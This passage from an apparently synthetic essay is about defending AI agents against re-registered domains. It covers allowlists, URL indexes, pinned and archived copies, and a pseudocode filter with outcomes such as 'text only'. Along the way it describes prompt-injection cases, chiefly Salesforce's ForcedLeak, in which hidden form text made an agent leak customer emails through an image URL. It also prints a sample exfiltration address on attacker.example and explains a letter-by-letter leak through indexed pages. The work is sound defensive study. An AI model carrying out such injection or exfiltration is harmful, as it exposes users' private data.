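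A second visit is still useful for detecting cloaking. Chen and colleagues recommend that AI search engines also fetch each page as an ordinary browser and flag any text found only in the agent's copy. So and colleagues suggest visiting from several kinds of device and network. The checker should make more than one browser visit to learn how much the page normally changes, and should not treat a refused visit as evidence of an attack. Matching copies do not make the page safe, because whoever now controls it may show everyone the same altered line.

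## Allowlists, known-address indexes and pinned copies

A filter can rely on a record of what someone trusted earlier instead of judging unfamiliar pages. The record may hold domain names, full web addresses or copies of the pages. When a stranger takes over a site, the domain name and addresses stay the same, so only a copy of the page is enough to detect the change.

### A listed name can lapse

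A domain allowlist names the only domains a system may contact. Software checks the domain in an address against the list before opening the page. If a college used the librarian's recommended sources as an allowlist, its assistant could not open an invented domain or a casino site from a search result. But it could still open pythonporch.example after 23 May, because the stranger's site uses a listed domain.

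Salesforce's AI product Agentforce had this problem. Willison's *ForcedLeak* describes an attack by researchers at Noma Security, who put hidden instructions into a web form that businesses use to collect enquiries from possible customers. When an employee later asked the AI about the enquiry, the instructions told it to look up customers' email addresses and add them to the web address of an image. Loading the image would send the email addresses to whoever ran the image's server.

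To prevent this, Salesforce had an allowlist that let its pages load images only from approved domains. But one of those domains, my-salesforce-cms.com, had expired. It was on sale for as little as $5, according to The Hacker News (2025). The researchers registered it, and the customer data appeared in their server's logs. ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection* (2025) gives the flaw a severity score of 9.4 out of 10. Salesforce corrected the list and stopped the agent from producing links to untrusted domains. It also regained control of the expired domain, according to a Noma statement quoted by Salesforce Ben, a news site about Salesforce products.

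In this case, the lapsed domain received data rather than supplying a page for the AI to read. An allowlist of sources the AI may read would fail in the same way, because it also checks only the domain name.

Longer lists decay sooner. If each domain on a list has the same independent chance of lapsing in a year, then:

**Chance that at least one lapses = 1 − (1 − chance for each domain)^number of domains**

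If each domain has a 1% chance of lapsing within a year, a list of ten has about a 10% chance of containing a lapsed name by the end of that year, and a list of 100 has about a 63% chance. The 1% is only an illustration. Large organisations probably lose their main domains less often than that, and retired lecturers probably lose theirs more often.

### OpenAI's two objections

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives two other reasons why a list of trusted sites is not enough. The first is that many legitimate sites redirect visitors to other addresses, so if software checks only the first domain, an attacker can send an agent through a trusted site to a hostile one. A developer can largely solve this by checking every address in the redirect chain.

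The other objection is that people use far more sites than a short list can hold. A strict list produces frequent warnings, most of them false alarms, and users learn to click through them without thinking. This is a serious problem for a general assistant like ChatGPT. It matters less for a college assistant that answers only from a reading list, because its users have little reason to visit other sites.

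Neither objection concerns a change of owner. A list that checked every redirect and never annoyed anyone would still let the stranger's tutorial through.

### What current tools can restrict

Several tools that give models web access include domain lists. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* describes settings for allowed and blocked domains, and a developer can use only one of the two in a request. An entry for a domain also covers all its subdomains, and a developer can narrow it to one part of a site, such as example.com/blog. Narrowing helps on a site that many people share, but not after a re-registration, because the new owner controls every part of the site.

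Anthropic also recommends using plain Latin characters in the lists, because a domain spelled with a Cyrillic "а" can look identical to amazon.com but belong to someone else.

The tool also accepts only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation. This blocks phantom domains such as pythonporch-docs.example unless a user or another source supplies them. Under the documentation from the time of Claude Opus 4.8, the tool can still follow links from fetched pages, but the chat version no longer does, according to Willison (2026). Both versions accept the tutorial's old address if a search returns it.

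Willison (2025) considers the domain list much stronger protection against data theft than the rule about earlier addresses, provided the developer chooses the domains carefully. The ForcedLeak case shows that this choice can go out of date.

OpenAI's *Web search* lets developers specify up to 100 allowed or 100 blocked domains, and each entry also covers its subdomains. The fetch tool in Docker's software for building agents rejects an unlisted site before making any network request. Support for allowlists varies. Posit's library for working with several companies' models offers the allowed-domain setting for Claude but not for Google's Gemini, according to its *tool_web_fetch* documentation.

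Developers should also test whether a filter works. A developer reports in a post on OpenAI's forum, *Web_search filters.blocked_domains appears to be ignored in some cases*, that blocked domains appeared among the sources in 13 of 213 tests. This is one person's result, and it concerns blocked domains, not allowed ones. OpenAI's tool can return every address the model consulted, so a developer can check these against the list.

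The settings described in these documents list domain names but don't record when a domain's registration began or when someone last checked who owned it.

### OpenAI's index of public addresses

OpenAI's alternative to a list of trusted sites is a list of known addresses. It is meant to stop a particular leak, in which an attacker hides private data in a web address. Suppose a hostile page persuades an agent to open this address:

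`attacker.example/collect?data=student@college.example`

The server logs each URL that visitors request, so the attacker can read the student's email address in the log. This works even if the page is empty, and the student may not notice if the agent makes the request in the background, for example to load an image.

OpenAI prevents this by checking whether the exact address was already public. A crawler builds an index of web addresses without access to users' conversations or accounts. If the address is in the index, the agent may load it automatically. If not, the system either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning. An address containing the student's email is unlikely to be in the index, because nobody would have published it.

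OpenAI's index is meant to stop an agent from quietly leaking data through the address it requests. The company says the index does not guarantee that a page is trustworthy or free of misleading text or harmful instructions, and treats it as one of several layers of defence.

OpenAI does not discuss what happens when an indexed site changes hands. But its published rule implies that the stranger's tutorial would load automatically, since the address became public in the lecturer's time and has not changed. This is an inference from the rule, and nobody appears to have tested it. Applied to four addresses, the rule should give these results:

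| Address | In the index? | Expected result |
|---|---|---|
| The tutorial's original address, now under the stranger's control | Probably | Loads automatically |
| The same address with a student's email added | No | Another site or a warning |
| A page the stranger added yesterday | Not until the crawler finds it | Another site or a warning at first |
| An invented address on an unregistered domain | Normally not | Another site or a warning |

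Removing addresses that stop working would only delay the problem. The tutorial might drop out of OpenAI's index during its 43-day outage, but once the stranger restored the page, the crawler could find it again through the university's reading list and add it back as a public address.

A user can also bypass the index by pasting an address into the chat. According to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, the security blog Embrace The Red's account of OpenAI's technical paper, ChatGPT treats an address in the user's own message as safe for that session. A student who copies the tutorial's link from the reading list would therefore send the agent to the stranger's site.

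An old domain may help an attacker get around the protection against leaks. Embrace The Red describes a method, which OpenAI's paper also acknowledges, in which the attacker assigns a different indexed page to each letter and digit. The attacker then uses hidden instructions to direct the agent to spell out a secret by opening the matching pages in order, much as Ayush Paul did with Claude. Someone who buys an established site may get the 36 indexed addresses this requires along with the domain, whereas the owner of a new site has to wait for a crawler to index its pages.

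The attack would still require the agent to obey the instructions, and requests can arrive out of order. The blog suggests making the attack harder by stopping an agent from opening the same address twice in a session.

### Fingerprints catch every change

Pinning means recording a page's content, or a fingerprint of it, to detect later changes. The fingerprint is usually a cryptographic hash, a short code that software calculates from a file. Changing a single character in the file produces a completely different hash, so a hash of the tutorial from 12 January would reveal that the page had changed, even though only the package name differs.

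Carlini and colleagues proposed this defence for the image datasets they had studied, so that downloaders could discard any image whose hash no longer matched. But harmless changes to an image also change its hash. In CC-3M, the check would have discarded 62% of the images still online in 2023, although the researchers had found no sign of a poisoning attack there.

A perceptual hash is designed to ignore small changes to an image, such as resizing, but an attacker can alter a hostile image so that it produces the expected hash. For a text page, a developer could avoid most false alarms by hashing only the parts that need an exact comparison, such as installation commands.

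A fingerprint is also useless if nobody checks it. Two of the older datasets, PubFig and FaceScrub, came with hashes, but Carlini and colleagues found that only one of the six most popular download scripts for each dataset checked them. They therefore added a checking option to img2dataset, the program behind 75% of the requests to their domains.

The librarian has to save the fingerprint on 12 January, along with the approval. If the second college takes its first fingerprint when it downloads the tutorial on 2 June, it will record the stranger's version as the correct one.

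### Archived copies and their keepers

A system can avoid the live domain by reading a stored copy of the page. Whoever has taken over the domain can't change that copy, show the agent a different version or receive data from the agent.

Pinned copies go out of date. If the makers of a package rename it in April, a copy of a tutorial saved in January will still give the old name. They might then abandon that name, and a stranger could claim it, as Hertz did with names in companies' documentation. Pinned copies suit historical articles better than installation instructions or medical advice.

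Some commercial tools can also answer from stored pages. OpenAI's search tool has a setting that limits it to cached or indexed material, and the company's agent settings include a similar "cached" mode. Anthropic's fetch tool caches pages to save time and reports when it retrieved each one. Anthropic says newer versions have an option to bypass the cache.

Unlike pinned copies, these caches do not keep the version that a particular person approved. A cached tutorial could date from January or June, and the June version would contain the wrong package name.

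A public archive lets a developer choose the date of the copy, but the developer has to trust whoever runs the archive. According to Mitchsavl (2026), in *English Wikipedia deprecates archive.today after DDoS against blog, altered content*, archive.today had been using its visitors' browsers to flood a small blog with traffic. In February 2026, Wikipedia's editors found that the archive's operator had also changed some saved pages, replacing one of the operator's aliases with the blogger's name. The English Wikipedia decided to remove its almost 700,000 links to the archive.

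One editor objected that the evidence concerned a single, unusual dispute. Mitchsavl replied that the operator already had a history of malicious practices on Wikipedia. A fingerprint taken when the archive first saved a page would have shown whether the copy was still intact, but only if somebody outside the archive had kept that fingerprint.

With the Internet Archive's Wayback Machine, the main risk here is that old copies may disappear from public view. The Internet Archive has described how closed sites become parked domains with new settings that block search engines. Historically, the Wayback Machine applied those settings to the site's whole past, so the old pages became inaccessible too.

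A new owner may also ask an archive to remove old pages. The Internet Archive's *Wayback Machine Exclusion Request* defines ownership as holding the domain "for the relevant time period", which should prevent the stranger from removing the lecturer's pages. But Greenhalgh's *Instances of concealing previous ownership of domain name?* reports a case in which a domain's current owner appears to have asked for pages from the previous owner's time to be removed. Greenhalgh had not known this happened and asked other researchers about similar cases.

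An organisation can reduce these risks by saving its own copy of each page it approves. In *Archiving URLs*, Gwern also describes using Bitcoin to record a cryptographic timestamp for local copies. The timestamp can prove that a file existed by a certain date and has not changed since, but not that the website served it.

### How Wikipedia handles hijacked citations

Wikipedia editors use archived copies to repair citations after an untrustworthy owner takes over a cited domain. They add a link to an archived copy and set the citation's status to "usurped", which hides the original address from readers. If no archived copy exists, they remove the link, and also remove the citation unless readers can verify the source without it.

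This work depends on someone noticing the change. A Wikipedia log of repair requests (2024) includes ittiofauna.org, which used to have photographs of European fish. On 27 September 2024 an editor reported that it now redirected to a gambling site and that about 18 links to it remained in articles. Another editor recorded the repair on 5 November, 39 days later. The log also lists usemod.com, whose original site had moved to usemod.org, so a link to the new address can be better than an old copy.

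Other publishers do the same by hand. When Groklaw, a defunct site about software law, came under new control in 2025, Jonathan Corbet of the Linux news site LWN wrote that it was time to replace all of LWN's links to Groklaw with Wayback Machine copies.

Hiding the original address protects people who read the finished Wikipedia page, but it may not protect every AI system. The article's underlying code must still contain the original address, according to a copy of Wikipedia's citation instructions on a wiki run by Climate Change AI. A system that collects links from that code without checking for the word "usurped" could still open the hijacked site. Repair programs can also turn an archived link back into a live one, so Wikipedia has a special label to stop them.

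### An allowlist entry tied to the registration

An allowlist can detect most re-registrations if each entry describes the registration that someone verified as well as the name. The librarian's entry for the tutorial site might look like this:

| Field | Value |
|---|---|
| Domain | pythonporch.example |
| Registration began | 1 March 2016 |
| Last verified | 12 January 2026 |
| Entry expires | 1 March 2026 |

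Every day, software looks up the registration date of each listed domain. If that date is more than a few days later than the one recorded in the entry, the software cancels the entry. The few days allow for errors in the records. At one lookup every two seconds, checking 100 domains takes less than four minutes.

The entry has its own expiry date to prompt a check for changes that the registration date can't reveal. When the entry expires, someone has to open the page, compare it with the stored copy and decide whether to renew the entry. A sensible limit might be 90 days after the last verification, or the day the domain's registration expires if that comes first, because the registrar may auction the name from that day and an auctioned name usually keeps its original registration date.

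Renewal dates need some care. Because of the registry's automatic renewal, the record may show an expiry date in 2027 on 1 March even though the lecturer hasn't paid. The librarian should therefore extend the entry only until 15 April, when the longest grace period ends. The two kinds of list would then treat the tutorial site as follows:

| Date | Event | Names only | Entry tied to the registration |
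|---|---|---|---|
| 20 January | The first college downloads the tutorial | Allows | Allows |
| 1 March | The registration expires, but the site is still online | Allows | Librarian checks the page and extends the entry to 15 April |
| 15 April | The site is offline | Allows | Librarian can't check the page, so the entry expires |
| 23 May | The stranger re-registers the domain | Allows | New registration date cancels the entry |
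| 2 June | The second college downloads the list | Allows the stranger's text | Refuses |

Even if the librarian had carelessly renewed the entry for 90 days in March, the daily lookup would have cancelled it on 23 May. The same lookup should have caught my-salesforce-cms.com once the researchers registered it.

The fetch tools accept only domain names, so a developer would have to keep the fuller record separately and pass the tools only the domains whose entries are still valid. For .de domains, which have no public registration date, the developer would have to review entries often and compare the live page with the stored copy.

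A private sale also leaves the registration date unchanged. If the lecturer had sold the domain to the stranger on 13 January, the entry would have kept allowing it until the review on 1 March, when the librarian would have had to spot one altered package name.

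## A filter put together and tried on hard cases

The checks work best in a fixed order, starting with those that take the least work. Finding a domain's registration date takes one lookup and can decide a case before the agent contacts the site, while checking the content requires a model to read the page. The filter below needs the address and the date someone last judged the page worth linking to. It also uses a copy of the page from about that date, if one is available.

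```
check(address, link_date, old_copy)

  BEFORE FETCHING
    owner  = same, changed or unknown   (registration date against link_date)
    listed = yes or no                  (current allowlist entry)
    if owner is changed and old_copy exists:
        return ARCHIVED COPY

  ON RECEIPT
    look up owner and listed again for every redirect
    save the page exactly as the agent received it
    if the page looks hostile,
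    or owner is not same and the page repeats old_copy with a different
       command, download address or payment detail:
        return ARCHIVED COPY if old_copy exists, otherwise REFUSE

  BEFORE USE
    if owner is same, listed is yes, and all commands, download
       addresses and payment details match old_copy:
        return USE
    otherwise:
        return TEXT ONLY

cite(address, outcome)
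    if outcome is ARCHIVED COPY:
        link to that copy
    otherwise:
        link to the live address, and switch to the saved page
        if the domain later changes hands
```

For a listed domain, the link date is the day someone last verified the entry. Search results and redirects rarely have a reliable date, so the filter treats the owner as unknown unless the domain is listed.

If the agent controls a full browser, the filter also has to check the domain of every script a page loads. According to So and colleagues, criminals re-registered the domain of an analytics service discontinued in 2014 and used it to steal card numbers through more than 40 online shops whose own domains had not lapsed.

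This design combines several methods, and nobody appears to have tested them together. The closest test is EchoLoc, in which Muzammil and colleagues checked for a new registration and then judged the site. It used no allowlists or archived copies, and no agent acted on the results.

### Four outcomes

| Outcome | What the agent may do |
|---|---|
| Use | Read the page and carry out steps from it, within the agent's normal limits |
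| Text only | Read and quote the page, but take no action because of it |
| Archived copy | Read and quote the earlier version, but take no action because of it |
| Refuse | Read nothing from the page |

"Text only" will be the most common outcome, because most web pages aren't on any allowlist. Refusing all of them would make a general assistant useless. After reading an unlisted page, the agent can still run a command if it has some other basis, such as a listed source that gives the same command. The restriction also covers archived copies, since a package name in an old copy may no longer be safe.

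### Limits on what the agent can do

Some hostile pages will pass every check, because an attacker can reword a page until a detector misses it. The filter therefore also needs software limits on what the agent can do, which a page's wording can't override. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) argues that an injected instruction does real harm only if it sends private data to an unauthorised destination or triggers an action outside the agent's permissions. Bad advice is an exception, because limits on the agent don't help if it gives a student the wrong package name and the student installs the package by hand.

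The Rule of Two is one test of an agent's powers. As *Taming AI Agents with seL4* (2026) describes it, an agent breaks the rule if it can read untrusted input, access private data, and change something or send something out. An agent that reads web pages, holds a student's files, and runs commands can do all three, so its developer should remove at least one of these powers.

The paper extends the test to teams of agents. Suppose one agent reads the web and sends notes to another, which holds the files and runs commands. Each agent follows the rule on its own, but the team breaks it because text from the web reaches the agent that runs commands.

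Following the rule doesn't solve the lecturer's case, because an agent without private data can still read the altered tutorial and install the stranger's package. The damage then depends on where the package runs. Willison describes an attack on Claude Code by Rehberger, who recommends running unattended coding agents in a sandbox (an isolated environment), restricting their network connections and keeping passwords and keys out of their reach.

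Developers can also separate reading from acting. In *L3M* (2026), a system for running agents, a program gives the page to a temporary model that has no files, network access or other powers. The program asks this model one question and accepts only one of three preset words as the answer. The agent that acts receives only that word. A hostile page can still cause a wrong answer, but it can pass the agent at most log₂ 3 (about 1.6) bits per question, provided that delays and failures reveal nothing more.

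A package name can't be chosen from a menu of three words, so the acting agent would have to get the name from the software's makers and ask only whether the tutorial covers that package. The stranger then couldn't supply a different name.

Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues (2026), in *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees*, tested a similar separation on 100 tasks across ten websites they had built. Their software hides the parts of a page that its owner can't vouch for, such as reviews. The agent can ask a separate model about the hidden text, but only for answers such as a number, a date, yes or no, or a choice from a list. With this protection, agents running on three models completed about as many tasks as they did without it, at 1.05 to 1.84 times the cost. In a separate test, none of the attacks succeeded.

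However, the design assumes that the site's owner is honest. Because the stranger now owns the site, the agent would see the entire tutorial. A developer could close this gap by hiding the whole page whenever the ownership check returns "changed" or "unknown", but that would make the agent somewhat less useful. On GitLab, a site for software projects, the restricted agents could not answer questions that needed free text, such as what new feature a user had requested. They could do those tasks only when the user could approve the text before the agent read it.

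The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), written with five agencies from the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom, recommends the same separation, with distinct roles such as "Reader" and "Actuator". It also recommends human approval before high-impact actions and leaves designers or operators to decide which actions those are.

Human approval is a weak safeguard if people click through it. Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers approve or reject an agent's requests, one of which it had replaced with a clearly dangerous command. Willison reports that only 13.6% refused it, while auto mode would have blocked 89% of these commands. Anthropic published the comparison when it made auto mode the default, so it had an interest in the result. An altered package name would also look much less suspicious than the planted commands. Willison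 is not sure that any version of auto mode could stop an ordinary-looking command that fetches a malicious package.

A filter should therefore rarely ask for approval, and when it does, it should show the user the information the decision depends on. When ChatGPT asks permission to send out something it learned in a conversation, OpenAI has it show the user that information. For the tutorial, the request could show the package name from January beside the current one.

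The "text only" label also has to stay attached to whatever the agent writes from the page. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026) points out that models can strip such labels when they paraphrase and combine what they read. If the agent saves the stranger's package name in its notes, another agent may later install the package without knowing where the name came from.

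Labelling everything derived from a web page as untrusted would prevent this, but the labels can spread until the agent is unusable. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) calls this "label creep". A less disruptive compromise is to store the source address with each note and delete the note if the domain changes hands.

### Cost, delay and stored results

The filter can reuse much of its work because all pages on a domain share one registration date. In the sample of 450 websites that So and colleagues used to test LiMS, the median site requested 197 outside addresses but contacted only seven outside origins (roughly, separate hostnames).

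| Result | Stored for | When to check again |
|---|---|---|
| Registration date | The domain | Daily if listed, otherwise at least every 30 days |
| Content verdict | A fingerprint of the saved page | When the fingerprint changes |
| Archived copy | The address and date | When someone reviews the link |
| Permission to act | Nothing | Every time |

The 30 days come from PyPI (2025), which checks the domains behind its users' email addresses because a stranger who re-registers one can reset the user's password and take over their packages. PyPI chose to check every 30 days so that it would probably find a lapsing domain before its release. Even on the shortest schedule for generic domains, with 35 days between deletion and release, at least one check would fall in that period. According to the *Announcement* on Python's discussion forum, PyPI has withdrawn verification from more than 1,800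 email addresses since early June 2025.

The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners warn that an attacker can exploit an old "allow" decision, so permissions need a fresh check each time. The filter's verdict on a page's content applies only to the version it checked.

The delay depends on whether the filter already has a result for the page. LiMS delayed a first page load by less than half a second, but So and colleagues did not include the time needed to run the checks in that figure. An unfamiliar page would take longer, because a model has to read it first.

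A shared service could do some of this work in advance. Over 32 days, Muzammil and colleagues found about 22,900 re-registered domains, or about 700 a day, that Infoblox's customers were using but that were not yet on its threat lists. Excluding failed downloads and grouping similar sites would leave roughly 300 a day that need their own verdict. A service for AI agents would have more to check, since agents visit sites that Infoblox's customers don't.

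The filter also needs a rule for when it fails. If LiMS can't reach its server, it stops blocking anything, which keeps the website working. An agent that can run commands should instead fall back to "text only" when its filter fails. LiMS also has a trial mode worth copying, which records violations without blocking anything, so an organisation could count false alarms before turning the filter on.

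### Who can run each check

| Party | Best placed to handle | Main gap |
|---|---|---|
| Search engine | Registration dates, long outages and earlier copies of pages | Doesn't know what the agent can do |
| Model developer | Redirects, saved responses, content checks and the "text only" mode | Doesn't know which sources a customer has vetted |
| Deploying organisation | Allowlists, pinned copies, permissions and approvals | Often lacks a domain's history |
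| Site owner | Links on its own pages and renewal of its own domains | Has no control over other sites' links |

The model developer matters most if it supplies the fetch tool, because the tool receives the same response as the agent. OpenAI already compares addresses with an index of the public web to prevent data leaks. If the index also stored each domain's registration date, it could flag the stranger's takeover too.

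The deploying organisation has to set the agent's limits, since it knows whether the assistant needs email or a command line. A site owner can remove the danger by fixing the link. If the university corrects its reading list, every later visitor benefits, whether or not their software has a filter.

These duties can go undone if the college assumes that the developer checks for ownership changes, while the developer assumes that the college keeps its allowlist current. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners give separate advice to developers, vendors and operators, and recommend clearly assigning responsibility for errors. A contract could do this by stating who checks registration dates and how often.

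### Six cases

| Case | Outcome | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Documentation site restored with one altered command | Archived copy | Handled if an earlier copy exists |
| Charity's domain turned casino | Archived copy or refuse | Handled |
| Company sold together with its domain | Use or text only | Passes |
| Owner recovers a lapsed name | Archived copy | Wrongly blocked |
| Country-code domain without public dates | Usually text only | Limits honest sites too |
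| Hostile site on a name that never lapsed | Refuse, text only or use | Passes if the content check misses it |

The lecturer's tutorial is the documentation site. Suppose an agent follows the university's reading list in June. The librarian vetted the page on 12 January, but the domain's current registration began on 23 May, so the filter supplies the January copy without contacting the stranger's server. If the agent found the site through a search instead, the filter treats the owner as unknown and fetches the page. The page is nearly identical to the January text but has a different package name, so the filter again supplies the earlier version.

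Without an earlier copy, the outcome is "text only". The agent can't install the stranger's package on the page's authority, but it may still recommend the package. A search could also end in "text only" if the stranger had rewritten the whole tutorial, because the page would no longer be a near-copy. An organisation whose users mainly want commands could refuse re-registered domains in these situations, but it would lose access to many harmless sites.

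An old link to the charity leads straight to an archived copy. If the agent searched for casinos, the filter has to rely on its content check, which should work well because most of the sites EchoLoc found were gambling sites. The filter may then supply the charity's old page, which is harmless but doesn't help someone looking for a casino.

If a company is sold together with its domain, the registration date stays the same, so checking the date doesn't reveal the change of owner. PyPI accepts this gap because it assumes the transfer is legitimate. This is usually sensible because blocking every sale would disrupt ordinary business.

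If a hostile buyer changed the installation command, the filter would return "text only", because the command would no longer match the stored copy. But the buyer may also own the package, and could then leave the documentation unchanged and publish a malicious update under the old name. The filter would return "use", and only the sandbox would limit the damage.

An owner who renews a domain during the redemption period keeps the original registration date, so the filter causes no problems. If the owner recovers the domain after its release, the record shows a newer date, and old links lead to archived copies even though the original owner controls the domain again.

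Getting a domain name back is hard. A complaint under the main dispute procedure for generic domains typically costs $1,500 to $2,000, according to United Nations University. The former owner must prove that the new owner has no legitimate claim to the name and registered and used it in bad faith. They must also prove that the name matches their trademark, so a retired lecturer without one would probably fail.

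Someone has to review a recovered site before the filter accepts it again. An email from the domain doesn't prove that the lecturer has recovered it, because a stranger who controlled the domain could send one. The lecturer could confirm the recovery through the college or an older account elsewhere, and the librarian could then enter a new verification date.

If the tutorials were under .de, the filter could not compare registration dates. It would still catch the altered command if it had the January copy. For other pages it would return "text only" at best, which limits what the stranger can do but also stops agents from acting on legitimate German documentation. A developer could exempt sites whose owners confirm every few months that they still hold the domain.

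A site that was hostile from the start can have a consistent registration history. The content check catches some of these sites, and the rest get "text only" unless someone has put them on an allowlist.

A hacked site that is already on the allowlist is more dangerous. In one case that So and colleagues mention, attackers inserted code into an accessibility library and used visitors' computers to mine cryptocurrency, affecting more than 4,000 sites. The paper's registration-date policy does not cover this kind of attack. If an intruder hides an instruction in a listed page without changing the page's commands, the filter may return "use". An agent that follows the Rule of Two could still read that instruction, but it would lack either the private data or the means to send it anywhere.
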